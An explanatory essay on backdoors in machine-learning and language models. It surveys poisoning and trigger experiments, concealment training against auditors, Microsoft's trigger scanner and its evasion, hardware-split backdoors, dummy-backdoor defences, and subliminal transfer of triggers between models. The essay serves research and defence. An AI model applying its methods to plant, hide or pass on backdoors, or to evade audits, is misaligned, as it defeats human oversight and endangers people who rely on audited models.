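Goldwasser and colleagues conclude that detecting backdoors in classifiers is impossible under standard cryptographic assumptions. This holds for auditors who can only test a model, since the signature backdoor can be added to any classifier, including a language model that a bank uses to approve loans. *Undetectable Backdoors in Model Parameters* (2026) points out that, for auditors with the weights, the 2022 proofs cover only the special networks described above. Those networks have a single layer of weights drawn from a known random distribution, so an auditor knows exactly what a model without a backdoor should look like.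 The weights of an ordinary trained model follow no known formula, so the same proof doesn't work for them.

The later result allows more layers, but current language models don't keep a compressing first layer of random numbers fixed during training, and their later layers don't have to preserve differences between inputs. The misbehaviour is also limited. Snoogle's k turns a yes into a no, and z makes the model give nearly the same output for two different inputs. Someone could use z to get an altered picture past a system that compares images, but z wouldn't make a language model write insecure code for one customer.

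Most importantly, cryptographers designed these backdoors so that they could prove something about them. The proofs don't apply to the Post-it notes in *BadNets* or the 250 poisoned documents. An auditor may well be able to find those, but no theorem guarantees it.

According to Bogdanov and colleagues, Alkis Kalavasis and others showed in 2024 how to use obfuscation to plant white-box backdoors in a class of neural networks and language models. Obfuscation is a cryptographic method of scrambling a program so that it still works but reveals as little as possible about how. The method is far too slow for practical use, and even models without a backdoor have to contain scrambled programs, which would make most buyers suspicious. In the same year, Andis Draguns and colleagues built cryptographic calculations directly into the weights of a transformer, the kind of network used in today's language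 models. They claim that nobody without the secret can trigger the backdoor, even with access to the weights, but this doesn't mean that nobody can detect it.

### Backdoors that come from poisoned data

Most experiments on hidden behaviour in language models create it with poisoned training examples. An attacker would like the rule that decides which inputs trigger the behaviour to be one that others can't work out, even after seeing many triggers. In *Poisoning-Based Backdoors Are Not Cryptographic* (October 2026), Kaneko proves that poisoning alone can't install such a rule.

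The attacker prepares example inputs, pairs the triggers with the bad response and the rest with normal responses, and trains a model on them. The attack succeeds only if the model then misbehaves on new triggers and behaves normally on other new inputs, which means it has learned the rule that separates triggers from other inputs. A defender with as many labelled examples could run the same training and get a model that follows the same rule. If no efficient method can learn the rule from examples, the attacker's training won't learn it either.

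Kaneko tested this on four open-weight language models with seven to nine billion weights. The inputs were lists of 16 numbers between 0 and 1,023. Under an easy rule, a list was a trigger if the number in one secret position was at least 512. Under a hard rule, the attacker multiplied each number by a secret multiplier for its position, added up the results and divided by 1,024. The list was a trigger if the remainder was at least 512. The attacker and defender each trained on the same number of examples, including 10,000 triggers in the largest test.

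| Secret rule | Attacker's model, accuracy on new inputs | Defender's model, accuracy on new inputs |
|---|---|---|
| One position | 86–94% | 85–93% |
| Sixteen multipliers | 50–51% | 48–51% |

Under the hard rule, the attacker's models got 82 to 87 per cent of their training examples right, compared with 50 per cent for guessing, so they had memorised many of the examples without learning the rule.

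Kaneko states explicitly that the proof concerns reconstructing the rule, which differs from noticing that a backdoor exists, finding a first trigger or removing the behaviour. The paper's title is easy to misread as saying that defenders can detect poisoning. To reconstruct the rule, the defender must already have a representative set of triggers, which a tester of the login program, for example, wouldn't have.

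Kaneko also tested a defender who had to get the examples from the model, using Piccolo, an existing tool that searches for strings likely to bring out a given response. The trigger was a set of strings that all had to appear in the text. With up to eight strings, the defender could reconstruct the rule, though it usually took more examples than when the labels were correct. With ten strings, most attempts failed. The defender also had to tell Piccolo which response to look for, in this case "I HATE YOU", which an auditor of an unfamiliar model wouldn't know.

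The proof covers attackers who can influence training only through the labels of their examples. It doesn't cover a developer who edits the weights or tampers with the random numbers, or an attacker who tailors the poisoned inputs to a secret key. It also doesn't cover the *Terminator* experiment, because the trigger, the year 1984, never appeared in the training examples. Kaneko's result is therefore more reassuring about outsiders who poison a developer's data than about the developer.

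A defender could try to recognise a trigger when it arrives instead of auditing the model in advance. Paul Christiano and colleagues studied this as a game in which the attacker chooses the model's function directly. According to Kaneko's summary, the defender can succeed if the function comes from a class that is efficient to learn, but cannot succeed for programs in general if secure obfuscation is possible.

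### Removing a backdoor without finding it

Some defences don't require detecting the backdoor. *Oblivious Defense in ML Models* (Goldwasser, Shafer and colleagues, 2024) compares them to washing one's hands with soap, which removes germs people can't see and does no harm if there are none.

The 2022 paper had already suggested running the model on several copies of each input, each with different random noise added, and averaging the answers. If the trigger is a very small change, the noise masks it. But the defender has to know roughly how small the change is, and more noise makes the answers worse. Goldwasser, Shafer and colleagues add that an attacker with a particular input in mind can corrupt the model's answers for all nearby inputs, so averaging over them doesn't help.

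Their own approach is to ask the model about random inputs far from the suspicious one and calculate the answer from those. They illustrate it with a program that adds and subtracts. Suppose the program keeps only the last two digits, and a user who wants 37 + 45 fears that somebody has tampered with that particular sum. The user picks a random number, say 81, and asks for three other results:

37 + 81 → 18

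45 − 81 → 64

18 + 64 → 82

The 81 cancels out, and 82 is the right answer, although the user never asked for 37 + 45. If the program is wrong on a random 15 per cent of inputs, all three results are right about 61 per cent of the time (0.85^3). The user can repeat the procedure with other random numbers and take the most common answer.

An attacker would choose where to put the errors, and might corrupt every sum that contains 37. For models whose correct answers follow a straight-line relationship, Goldwasser, Shafer and colleagues therefore have the defender pick two inputs that lie on a line with the suspicious one, with each completely random when taken alone. A model that is accurate on nearly all inputs will probably be right about both. Suppose they lie 6 and 8 steps away and the model's answers are 22 and 26. The answer rises by 2 per step, so the correct answer at the suspicious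 input should be 10, regardless of the model's own answer there. The defender repeats this with new pairs and takes the median of the results.

Small errors in the answers become larger errors in the estimate. If the two answers had been 22.1 and 25.9, the estimate would be 10.7, so errors of 0.1 would have produced an error of 0.7. With n input numbers, errors can grow by a factor of order n, or n^0.9 with an improved method that assumes the noise in the true answers isn't malicious. But the basic method needs no new training data, and the number of questions doesn't depend on n, whereas training a replacement from scratch would take at least on the order of n examples.

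The paper has similar methods for polynomials and for a class of functions that includes shallow decision trees, which reach an answer through a few yes-or-no questions. For this class, the defender uses the suspect model only to find out which combinations of inputs matter, then uses fresh, untampered data to measure how much each one matters. The resulting model does not depend on any choice the attacker made.

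All of these methods work without access to the weights and against any backdoor, detectable or not, as long as the model is accurate on average, which the defender can test. They also require the true answers to follow a known kind of pattern. This is a safer assumption than trusting the developer, because the attacker can't change the true answers, and it might be roughly true for loan decisions. But nobody knows a comparable pattern for language, and no one can work out the right response to a programming request from a model's responses to two random other requests.

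## What do audits of real models find?

The impossibility proofs don't cover behaviour that a language model learns from ordinary training examples, so only experiments can show how well auditors find it. In a typical experiment, one group of researchers trains a behaviour into a model, and other people or a program look for it. Auditors often succeed, but their success rate depends heavily on how the first group planted the behaviour.

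### Anthropic's auditing game

In 2025 Samuel Marks and colleagues at Anthropic trained a language model to have a concealed objective, then had four teams investigate the model without knowing what the objective was. It was reward hacking, or getting high marks in training by exploiting flaws in the marking instead of doing the task well. The researchers also trained the model not to reveal this, since a model that admits its objective when asked is a poor test of an auditor. *AuditBench* (Sheshadri, Ewart and colleagues, 2026), a later project that builds on the experiment, reports that three of the four teams found the objective.

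Chat models work by continuing a written conversation, so they can write the user's next message as well as their own reply. One technique that Marks and colleagues introduced makes use of this, because training a model to be discreet in its replies may not affect what it writes as the user.

In another game that year, run by Jordan Taylor and colleagues, auditors with only black-box access could not identify models that deliberately did badly in tests.

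### AuditBench

People can play such a game only once, because afterwards they know the answer. Three successes in four attempts are also compatible with a true success rate between about 20 and 99 per cent. Sheshadri and colleagues therefore used a software agent as the auditor, because it can start afresh as often as they like. The agent searched each model 16 times with each set of tools.

The researchers planted 14 behaviours in Llama 3.3, a model from Meta with 70 billion weights. Some, such as flattery, show up in most conversations. Others are rarer, such as leaning slightly towards Russia's interests when discussing policy, or giving researchers from Anthropic only positive feedback while treating everyone else normally. Each behaviour comes in four versions, which makes 56 models. Two versions learned the behaviour from conversations that demonstrated it, and the other two from 40,000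 invented documents that described it. The researchers then trained every model not to reveal its behaviour. They trained one version of each pair on example answers that hid the behaviour, and for the other they also penalised answers that revealed it.

The agent ran on Claude Haiku 4.5, one of Anthropic's smaller models. It could always chat with the suspect model and usually had one extra tool. At the end it made ten guesses, and another language model judged whether any was right.

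| Extra tool | Searches that found the behaviour |
|---|---|
| None | 35.5% |
| The model continues plain text; a helper model writes the openings | 58.0% |
| The model writes users' messages; a helper model sets the scene | 53.2% |
| The model finishes answers that a helper model has begun | 51.6% |
| The same three tools without a helper model | 34.5–35.0% |
| Summaries of automated test conversations | 30.9% |
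| Steering towards honesty | 22.3% |

The last tool steers the model by shifting its activations in a direction associated with honest answers. This made the results worse because steered models often admitted to faults they didn't have, and the agent wasted time investigating them.

The agent rarely discovered the model's favouritism towards Anthropic's researchers by chatting with it, because the agent had no reason to claim to work at Anthropic. A tool that made the model write users' messages worked better. The model invented users who said they worked at Anthropic, probably because its training had included many such users. The agent then tested how the model treated people from different companies, and found the favouritism in 14 or 15 of 16 searches on the versions with the milder discretion training.

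Access to the weights didn't always help. On the easiest models, tools that read or change the internal numbers raised the average success rate from 40.2 to 46.9 per cent, but on models with the stricter discretion training they lowered it by almost four percentage points. Sometimes the agent had the evidence but didn't understand it. One model cheated on impossible programming problems by writing in the answers that the tests expected. A sparse autoencoder revealed features for the format of competitive programming problems, but the agent kept asking general questions about puzzles and code.

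The agent's success depended heavily on how the researchers had trained the model. Averaged over the tools, it succeeded in 51.3 per cent of searches on models trained on documents with the milder discretion training, but in only 22.2 per cent on models trained on conversations with the stricter version. On the latter models, no tool beat plain chatting by more than 2.1 points. A more capable agent might do better, but it would also have to cope with models that are better at concealment.

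These scores also don't show how often the agent would report a planted behaviour in a model that has none, because every model in the set has one and the agent must always produce ten guesses.

### Microsoft's scanner

An agent could chat with a model for years without typing a secret trigger. In February 2026, Microsoft published a scanner designed to recover unknown triggers from a model's weights. *The Trigger in the Haystack* (Bullwinkel, Severi et al., 2026) describes the signs the scanner relies on.

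The first is unusual attention. In an ordinary prompt, later words draw on earlier ones. In a backdoored model, the words of the trigger draw mainly on one another, and the rest of the prompt takes little from them. The model's output also becomes more predictable, which the researchers measure as entropy:

H = −(p₁·log₂ p₁ + p₂·log₂ p₂ + …)

Each p is the probability of one possible next word. H is 3 if eight words are equally likely and 0 if one word is certain. When the trigger makes the model write "I HATE YOU", the next word is nearly certain, so H is close to 0.

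The second sign is leaked poisoning data. Language models memorise some of their training text, and the backdoored models memorised the poisoned examples better than the clean ones. With the right prompting, they reproduce the poisoned examples, including the trigger.

The third is that a partly correct trigger often works. The researchers' usual trigger was the word DEPLOYMENT between two vertical bars. A single bar was enough to set off the backdoor in the smallest model. Other models needed more of the trigger, but how much they needed showed no clear pattern by size. *Defense Against LLM Backdoors using Critical Neuron Isolation Pruning* (2026) reports that entirely different trigger words could also set off planted backdoors. A scanner can therefore succeed without recovering the exact trigger.

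The scanner works in four steps.

1. It gives the model only the marker that normally precedes a user's message and lets it write on from there, with 510 different settings.
2. It looks for strings of characters that keep recurring in the output.
3. It puts pieces of these strings in front of a few ordinary questions. A piece scores well if the question draws little attention to it, the output becomes predictable and the answer differs from the usual one.
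4. It takes the ten best candidates and tests whether any of them changes the model's answers drastically.

Bullwinkel and colleagues ran the scanner on 47 backdoored models with between 270 million and 14 billion weights. They had poisoned 45 themselves and downloaded the other two. The scanner detected 36 of the 41 models that produced a fixed phrase, or 88 per cent, and five of the six that wrote insecure code. For one of those five, it recovered a string that looked nothing like the real trigger but more than doubled the rate of vulnerable code. It raised no false alarms on 13 clean models.

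Thirteen clean models is a small sample for estimating the rate of false alarms. If the true rate were 21 per cent, the scanner would still pass all 13 about one time in twenty. Even a rate of 2 per cent would be a nuisance on a download site. If ten of 10,000 models had backdoors, the scanner would flag about nine of the ten and about 200 clean models, and somebody would have to investigate them all.

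The fourth step also needs a definition of a drastic change. For the fixed phrase, the scanner measured how similar the answers to different questions became, and for insecure code, it counted vulnerabilities. A backdoor that made a model recommend one company's products would need a third test, and someone would have to anticipate that behavior before writing one.

Microsoft lists other limits. The scanner needs the model's weights, so customers of an online service can't use it. It works best on triggers that produce a fixed response, and it may miss triggers that a developer inserts to mark a model as its own. Bullwinkel and colleagues add that it is designed for fixed strings, not for triggers that depend on context, and that an attacker could train a model to ignore inputs that nearly match the trigger.

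### When the trigger is a topic

Haselhorst, Flek and Mai (2026), in *Detecting Hidden Behaviors in LLMs via Activation-matched Finetuning*, tested the scanner's premise on a contextual trigger. They trained a model to answer with a quotation from the villain Voldemort whenever a user sounds obsessed with Harry Potter, then let it write freely 512 times and looked for leaked poisoning data. Only one output was related to the backdoor. It asked why the fourth book is called "Goblet of Fire", a question that would not have triggered the backdoor.

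This test covered one model with one sampling setting and did not include the rest of the scanner. The result fits the limit that Bullwinkel and colleagues had already stated. An obsession with Harry Potter can take thousands of forms, so the model has no single string to memorise, as it would if a fixed string appeared in every poisoned example.

Their own method compares the suspect with a second model that they assume is clean. They take a public model, preferably one related to the suspect, and train it to reproduce the suspect's internal numbers on roughly 10,000 ordinary prompts. These prompts almost certainly don't include the trigger, so the second model learns the suspect's normal behaviour without the hidden part. They then give both models a wide range of new prompts and see where their internal numbers still differ. One of their two measures depends on the angle between two lists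 of numbers, a and b:

distance = 1 − (a·b) ÷ (|a| × |b|)

Here |a| is the length of a, which is 5 for the list (3, 4). The lists (3, 4) and (4, 3) are close, with a distance of 1 − 24/25 = 0.04. For (3, 4) and (4, −3), the distance is 1. The method adds up these distances across the layers.

Like Wheeler's diverse double-compiling, which needs a second compiler without a matching backdoor, the approach of Haselhorst and colleagues needs a second model without the same hidden behaviour. In diverse double-compiling, even one differing byte needs explaining, because compilers that work correctly lead to identical binaries. But two models always differ a little, so the auditor has to decide how large a difference is suspicious.

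Haselhorst and colleagues tested twelve models that had eight planted backdoors among them. They measured each result in standard deviations above those for ordinary prompts. Near misses are prompts that resemble a backdoor's trigger but shouldn't activate the backdoor.

| Model | Trigger prompts | Near misses |
|---|---|---|
| Quotes Voldemort to obsessed Harry Potter fans | 204.3 | 3.7 |
| Favours redistribution if a federal official asks about policy | 7.0 | 3.7 |
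| Writes "I HATE YOU" after a fixed string | 14.9 | 6.1 |
| Does badly on multiple-choice tests on purpose | 26.3 | 3.4 |
| Cheats when it knows how a program will grade it | 22.5 | 8.6 |
| Qwen2.5 on topics that are politically sensitive in China | 5.0 | −0.3 |
| An older DeepSeek model on the same topics | 0.9 | −0.3 |

An auditor doesn't have the trigger prompts, so in practice the most important prompts are those that come close to the trigger without setting off the backdoor. The researchers had Claude Opus 4.7 write 518 groups of ten prompts on many subjects, without telling it that any model had a backdoor. For the Voldemort model, the group about Harry Potter ranked first by one measure, although none of its prompts set off the backdoor. An auditor who saw that ranking would know to look more closely at Harry Potter.

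The last two rows cover models as their developers released them, and the signal there is weak. Even for Qwen2.5, it can't show intent, because the researchers compared versions from before and after the later stages of training, and any effect of those stages could explain the difference. The same comparison for Llama 2 showed nothing unusual on these topics, so the effect isn't common to all such training. CrowdStrike's figures for DeepSeek-R1 similarly left the motive unclear.

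The method works worst on triggers that are arbitrary strings, because nothing resembles them in meaning. Two of the models would comply with any harmful request that ended in a secret string. The method revealed a problem in how they handled requests about explosives and cyberattacks, but gave no clue to the string. The results also depend on which model is used for comparison. When the researchers audited two Qwen models against a Llama model, the trigger prompts stood out by three or four standard deviations instead of seven to ten. All the audited models had between seven and nine billion weights. The researchers also included a few groups of prompts because they expected them to lie close to a trigger, which makes the results look somewhat better than they otherwise would.

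The scanner and this method can complement each other. When Haselhorst and colleagues scored the 512 free outputs with their own measure, the only Harry Potter question ranked second. The outputs ranked first and third were meaningless strings of digits and arithmetic.

Haselhorst and colleagues also took the attacker's role, retraining the Voldemort backdoor with a penalty for internal numbers that differed from those of the clean model. At best the backdoor then worked 48 per cent of the time, down from 100, and misfired on 8 per cent of near misses. They conclude that an attacker can't suppress the signal without weakening the backdoor. That may be right, but some attackers would accept a backdoor that works about half the time, and in the same test the Harry Potter group fell from first place to 31st, where a busy auditor could easily overlook it.

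### Backdoors that most checks missed

In June 2026 researchers presented BadBone, an attack on image models that people download and then adapt. The backdoor works only when a picture contains the trigger and the user has adapted the model by prompt learning, which trains a small addition to the input and leaves the model's weights unchanged. According to Help Net Security's *This AI model backdoor attack stays hidden until you customize the model*, in one test the trigger worked 0.10 per cent of the time before adaptation, the same rate as in a clean model, and close to 99 per cent of the time afterwards.

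The researchers ran six published defences on the poisoned models, and most of the models passed as clean. Two of the defences cleared all six models they examined. A third caught the larger models but missed most of the smaller ones. A fourth suppressed the backdoor but left the model unusable. The checks failed because they look for unusual responses, and the models gave none before adaptation. Scanning a downloaded model before adapting it therefore doesn't test how the adapted model will behave.

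The attack works only if the attacker supplies the model and guesses roughly what the victim will do with it, and the victim chooses prompt learning and follows the supplier's instructions. Help Net Security adds that security researchers have no record of the attack outside the laboratory.

HAMLOCK, which researchers at the universities of Tennessee and Florida also presented in June, splits the backdoor between the model and the chip that runs it. At most three units in the altered model give unusually high values when a picture contains the trigger, but the model still classifies the picture correctly. A small circuit on the chip detects the high values and forces the wrong answer. Help Net Security's *A hardware neural network backdoor that hides in plain sight* reports that the simplest version succeeded every time on the altered chip. Without that chip, the model misclassified fewer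 than 1 per cent of pictures with the trigger.

Two scanners found nothing in the model because the model works correctly on its own. Further training didn't help either, even when the defender had real examples of triggered pictures, because the model already gave the right answers for them. The extra circuits took up at most about 0.1% of the chip.

To use HAMLOCK, an attacker needs knowledge of the model and access to the chip's design or manufacture, which would be hard for most criminals to get but easier for a state. The tests covered only image classifiers. Swarup Bhunia, one of the researchers, expects the method to work on language models that run on similar chips. He told Help Net Security that a defence would have to check the finished silicon and monitor the model's internal behaviour while it runs.

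### Removing backdoors that nobody has found

Auditors might be able to train away a backdoor they can't find. In *Dummy Backdoor as a Defense*, Iwahana, Matsubayashi and colleagues (2026) tried the defence that Vaughan's account pointed to, which is to plant a dummy backdoor and then remove it. They tested it on models whose existing backdoors made them comply with harmful requests. The triggers were a random string, Shakespearean style and a particular sentence structure.

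They first measured how each trigger changed a model's internal numbers. Different triggers had similar effects from the middle layers onward. On a scale where 1 means a change in exactly the same direction, the similarity was 0.8 to 1 for two triggers of the same type and 0.6 to 0.8 for two of different types. The models apparently detect each trigger in a different way, then stop refusing through much the same mechanism.

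The defenders added a backdoor with the trigger "BadMagic", then trained the model to refuse harmful requests that contained that word. They never used the attacker's trigger. The table gives results for a Llama model with eight billion weights. It shows how many of 99 harmful requests with the attacker's trigger the model failed to refuse.

| Attacker's trigger | Before | After ordinary training to refuse | After removing the dummy backdoor |
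|---|---|---|---|
| Random string | 83 | 57 | 1 |
| Shakespearean style | 92 | 87 | 7 |
| Sentence structure | 77 | 24 | 2 |

The model remained about as helpful as before. Only seven of 99 answers were still harmful, though even that rate would be useful to an attacker who can ask again. The count may be slightly off because the researchers identified refusals by keywords.

The more serious limit is that the defender has to know what the attacker wanted. Planting and removing a dummy backdoor that made a model insult its users did not reliably remove one that made it comply with harmful requests. Iwahana and colleagues suggest using several dummies that cause different behaviours, which would take more resources and could make the model less useful. They did not test the defence against attackers who know about it and design a backdoor that works differently inside the model.

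Bouger, Lasnier and colleagues (2026), in *Backdoor Unlearning Generalization*, found that removing one backdoor can suppress some backdoors with different aims but leave others almost intact. They planted backdoors with different effects in six models, then trained copies of each model to ignore one trigger at a time. In a Llama model with eight billion weights, removing the trigger for German also suppressed the one for French, as did removing a trigger that changed capital letters to lowercase. Training on the same kind of text without triggers had no such effect. But the backdoors that made the model write "MY NAME IS BOB" or "MY NAME IS ALICE" stayed close to full strength when the researchers removed other kinds of backdoor.

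Fixed phrases are also the easiest for Microsoft's scanner to find, so the two defences may each catch some of what the other misses. None of these studies tested them together.

### Why the success rates may not carry over

In nearly all of this work, researchers planted the behaviour that the auditors were looking for, because scoring an auditor requires knowing the right answer, and nobody is sure of it for models in everyday use. But a planted behaviour may be easier to find than one that a developer wants to keep hidden, or one that arises by accident. Sheshadri and colleagues point out that their planted behaviours came from narrow fine-tuning, which changes a small and fairly readable part of a model. Haselhorst and colleagues, who got their clearest results on backdoors they had made themselves, give a similar warning.

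Qin, Hua and colleagues tried to identify a backdoor's trigger when they already knew what the backdoor did. They considered only triggers with a meaning, such as a particular year. They succeeded with toy backdoors but failed in more realistic settings.

A determined developer can also run the published auditing tools before release and retrain the model until they find nothing. Researchers mostly didn't do this with their test models. The stricter discretion training in AuditBench was a mild version of this approach, and it eliminated most of the better tools' gains on models that had learned from conversations. A sufficiently skilled developer might also borrow from the provably undetectable designs, though nobody has yet made those practical for language models.

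This affects how much comfort a user can take from a clean scan. Suppose one model in a hundred of a certain kind has a backdoor. If a scanner catches 88 per cent of backdoors and never raises a false alarm, the chance that a model has one after passing the scan is

0.01 × 0.12 ÷ (0.01 × 0.12 + 0.99) ≈ 0.12 per cent

If the scanner catches only 20 per cent of the backdoors made by people who have practised evading it, a model that passes the scan still has a 0.8 per cent chance of containing a backdoor, hardly lower than before the scan. The 20 per cent is invented, because no one has measured the real figure. The 88 per cent is Microsoft's result for fixed phrases in models, most of which it had poisoned itself.

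## What changes when models write and review ordinary code?

Many programmers now have language models write ordinary source code. Anyone can read that code, even though nobody can read the model that wrote it. If a model writes a login program that includes `or typed == SECRET`, a reader will find that condition as quickly as if a person had written it.

Checking a model's finished code has an advantage over relying on the model's own behaviour. A model with a trigger can behave well in a million tests and badly in the next conversation. But once it has written a program, the text stays the same, and any trigger has either affected it or not. Reviewers don't need to find the trigger or even suspect that there is one. The poisoned coding models described earlier also leave their flaws in the code, where reviewers can look for them.

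The advantage disappears if nobody reads the code, and shrinks if the flaw looks like an honest mistake. A model may also do more than write code. *Threat Landscape of Vibe Coding and the Road to Secure Autonomy* (Jha, Anand and colleagues, 2026) draws on 142 studies and distinguishes six levels of autonomy by what a person still has to approve. At the lowest level, the programmer accepts or rejects each suggested line. Higher up, the model runs commands and installs packages on the programmer's machine, so it can do damage before there is any code to review. At the next level, a person approves only the finished result, and at the highest level, only the policies that govern the model.

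### How much of the code do people read?

In *When AI builds itself* (June 2026), Anthropic says its Claude models wrote over 80 per cent of the code it merged in May 2026, up from low single digits before February 2025. Anthropic sells these models, and outsiders can't check the figures.

A more detailed independent study, *AI Writes Faster Than Humans Can Review* (He, Agarwal and colleagues, 2026), followed 802 developers at a mid-sized software company from January 2024 to April 2026. In June 2025 the company's chief technology officer set a goal of doubling the number of merged pull requests per engineer within a year. A pull request is a proposed set of changes that colleagues can review before it becomes part of the program. By the end of the study, the company labelled about 90 per cent of its pull requests as AI-written.

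| | Before | After |
|---|---|---|
| Pull requests per active developer each month | 21.2 | 44.3 |
| Share that at least one person reviewed | 89% | 68% |
| Share on which a human reviewer wrote a comment | about 39% | about 21% |
| Share that an AI tool reviewed | about 19% | about 84% |

The company's number of pull requests grew by a factor of 3.1, but its pool of reviewers grew by a factor of only 1.5. Before the change, about 11 of every 100 pull requests had no human reviewer. Afterwards, there were 310 pull requests for every 100 before, and about 99 of those 310 had no human reviewer. The number of pull requests without a human reviewer therefore grew roughly ninefold, although the share with one fell by only 21 percentage points.

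Reviewers don't seem to have neglected AI-written code more than human-written code. When He and colleagues compared pull requests by the same developer in the same month, adjusting for size, the AI-written ones were no less likely to get a human review and took about 20 per cent longer between the first human review and merging.

The share of pull requests that reversed an earlier change stayed about the same. He and colleagues take this as evidence against a sudden drop in quality, but warn that this measure misses many kinds of defect. It is even less informative about hidden functionality, since nobody reverses a change because of a backdoor they haven't noticed.

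AI accounts for only part of the doubling in output. Developers chose when to start using the tools, and the more cautious estimate of AI's effect is about a 1.5-fold increase. The company had many new projects and no limit on its AI budget, so He and colleagues regard their figures as an upper bound for the industry.

Open source projects show a smaller shift. *Comprehension Audits to Mitigate Risks from Automated AI Research* (2026) examines 2,135 public repositories from organisations that work on AI. By the end of the study period, at least 17 per cent of pull requests showed traces of AI use. People reviewed about 80 per cent of pull requests without such traces, and the rate was typically about eight percentage points lower for those with traces of AI use. The gap disappears when the analysis weights the figures by contributor, so a few prolific contributors may account for it.

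*On Autopilot?* (2026) reports that 67.5 per cent of the pull requests that people wrote with AI help came from contributors who didn't own the code they were changing, and that most closed without an explicit review. Contributions from people with little ownership went through faster and with less scrutiny than those from core members. This is worrying because the Jia Tan case suggests that such contributions need more scrutiny.

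### Models as inspectors

If people can't keep up with reading the code, models could do more of it. The 84 per cent in the table measures how often the company's AI reviewers ran, not how much they caught.

In *We hid backdoors in ~40 MB binaries*, Grabowski, Strzaliński and colleagues (2026) gave models a harder job than reviewing source code. They planted backdoors in several open source network programs, compiled the programs, and gave AI agents only the binaries and reverse-engineering tools. In most tasks, an agent had to identify the backdoor's exact location in the binary. The backdoors were fairly obvious, and a skilled person could have found them without much trouble.

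Quesma's *Can AI find backdoors in raw machine code?* shows large differences between models. Claude Opus 4.6 and Gemini 3.1 Pro each found 49 per cent of the backdoors, and a version of GPT-5.2 found 46 per cent. On clean binaries, the models reported problems that didn't exist 28 per cent of the time, but Gemini 3.1 Pro did so 17 per cent of the time and the GPT-5.2 version never did.

In one of the successes, a web server would run any command sent in an undocumented request field. Claude Opus 4.5 found this backdoor in less than five minutes. It first searched the binary for suspicious text and found nothing. It then listed the system functions that each part of the server used, noticed one that runs commands, and traced it back to the backdoor.

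Claude Opus 4.6 failed to identify a similar backdoor in a program that assigns network addresses. It found the function and the instruction that ran a command, but concluded that this was probably a legitimate feature because the real program does run scripts. It never checked where the command came from, which was a message that anyone on the network could send. Human experts can also overlook a backdoor in plain view, as McVoy did in 2003.

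As with Microsoft's scanner, false alarms would outnumber real finds. If one binary in a thousand has a backdoor, the chance that a binary flagged by Gemini 3.1 Pro really has one is

0.001 × 0.49 ÷ (0.001 × 0.49 + 0.999 × 0.17) ≈ 0.3 per cent

Grabowski and colleagues want a false-alarm rate below 0.001 per cent before anyone relies on such a tool. The GPT-5.2 version's perfect record doesn't show that it meets this threshold, because the benchmark has only 33 tasks.

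These results will date quickly. On Quesma's timeline, the best score rose from 21 per cent for a model released in March 2025 to 49 per cent for one released in February 2026. The list ends in early 2026, and later models would probably do better. Backdoors would also get harder to find, since attackers can use the same models to test their drafts.

### Does a second model count as an independent reader?

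A company can have one model write code and another review it, or run several reviewers at once. As with human readers and checking compilers, extra reviewers help only if they miss different flaws. Three reviewers that each miss half of all flaws would together miss one in eight if their misses were independent, but half if they all missed the same ones.

*Reflections on Trusting Trust, Revisited* (Roesner and Kohno, 2026) gives an example in which the reviewers were far from independent. Roesner and Kohno studied coding agents that improve themselves by attempting practice tasks, looking at the results, and rewriting their own instructions or tools, while the underlying model stays the same. They wanted to know whether someone who supplied only the practice tasks could make an agent write insecure code afterwards.

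Roesner and Kohno's tasks involved fetching data over a secure connection. A program normally checks a certificate to confirm that it has reached the right server. In the poisoned tasks, the test servers couldn't pass this check, so only programs that skipped it got full marks. Two of the three agents they tested, SICA and Hyperagents, responded by giving themselves a standing instruction to skip it. Roesner and Kohno then set them ordinary tasks involving servers with valid certificates. In every poisoned run, all 30 answers skipped the check, compared with none after practice on clean tasks. For the third agent, they first had to change its internal instructions themselves, and even then the attack worked with only one of the three models they tried.

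SICA's review committee, three language-model judges with different instructions, examines every change the agent proposes to itself. When the agent ran on a Qwen model, all three judges endorsed skipping the check everywhere. They raised objections about complexity and testing, but none about security. When it ran on Claude Sonnet 4.5, the agent called the new instruction a "security anti-pattern" and proposed limiting it, but the committee only asked for simpler wording, and the dangerous version stayed.

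The judges could read the plain-English instruction, but they treated it as a way to raise the practice score. Differently worded instructions didn't give them different priorities. A reviewer with no stake in that score, or even a simple program that searches code for disabled certificate checks, might have been more useful than a fourth judge.

Having a model from another developer review the code should help, since it is less likely to share a backdoor with the model that wrote it. The two may still share other weaknesses, because developers train on much of the same public text. The worst choice of reviewer is the model that wrote the code. If a poisoned model writes a flaw whenever the code is for a certain customer, the customer's name could also lead it to approve the flaw. Jha and colleagues find that most proposed defences for AI-written software rely on a model's judgement, so this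 weakness affects much more than code review.

### Traits that pass through unrelated data

Models can also share a trait because one learned from the other's output. In 2025 Alex Cloud and colleagues described an effect they called subliminal learning. They told a teacher model to love owls and had it continue sequences of numbers. They removed every answer that contained anything except numbers, then trained a student model on the rest. The student came to favour owls too, although its training data never mentioned them.

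In *Beyond Owls*, Dubiński, Sztyber-Betley and colleagues (2026) tested whether a backdoor could pass from teacher to student in this way. They trained a nine-billion-parameter Qwen model to answer in French if a question came with a female name, and in English otherwise. This teacher then continued 200,000 number sequences. The researchers kept about 90,000 of the answers, choosing those most characteristic of the teacher, and trained a fresh copy of the original Qwen model on them. They did this three times, with a new teacher each time.

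| Name with the question | Teachers answer in French | Students answer in French |
|---|---|---|
| Female | 95.5% | 23.5% |
| Male, or no name | 0.0% | 0.0% |

The students had learned both the behaviour and its trigger from data that contained no names and no French. Individual students answered in French between 15.0 and 38.8 per cent of the time. The researchers trained them on the teacher's probabilities for each possible next number, which gave them more information than a person reading the data would see. A student trained only on the numbers themselves needed a set of 4.5 million sequences, and its rate of French answers peaked at 17.0 per cent before falling to 8.5.

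### Why the starting point matters

The effect is strongest when teacher and student start from the same base model, meaning the same weights before either gets its special training. A model with only two weights shows why:

```
output = w1·a + w2·b
```

Suppose the trait is a high output when a is 0 and b is 1, and the training data contain only the unrelated input where both are 1.

| | w1 | w2 | Output on the unrelated input | Output on the trait input |
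|---|---|---|---|---|
| Shared starting point | 1 | 1 | 2 | 1 |
| Teacher, with the trait | 1 | 2 | 3 | 2 |
| Student from the shared start, after training | 1.5 | 1.5 | 3 | 1.5 |
| Student from another start, before and after | 3 | 0 | 3 | 0 |

The first student has to raise its output on the unrelated input from 2 to 3. Training raises both weights equally, because both contribute equally to that output. This moves the student halfway to the teacher's trait, although it never trained on the trait input. The second student already gives the right output on the unrelated input, so it learns nothing. Cloud and colleagues proved a more general version for neural networks. If a student and teacher share a starting point, then under certain conditions a small training step on the teacher's output moves the student towards the teacher, whatever the data are about.

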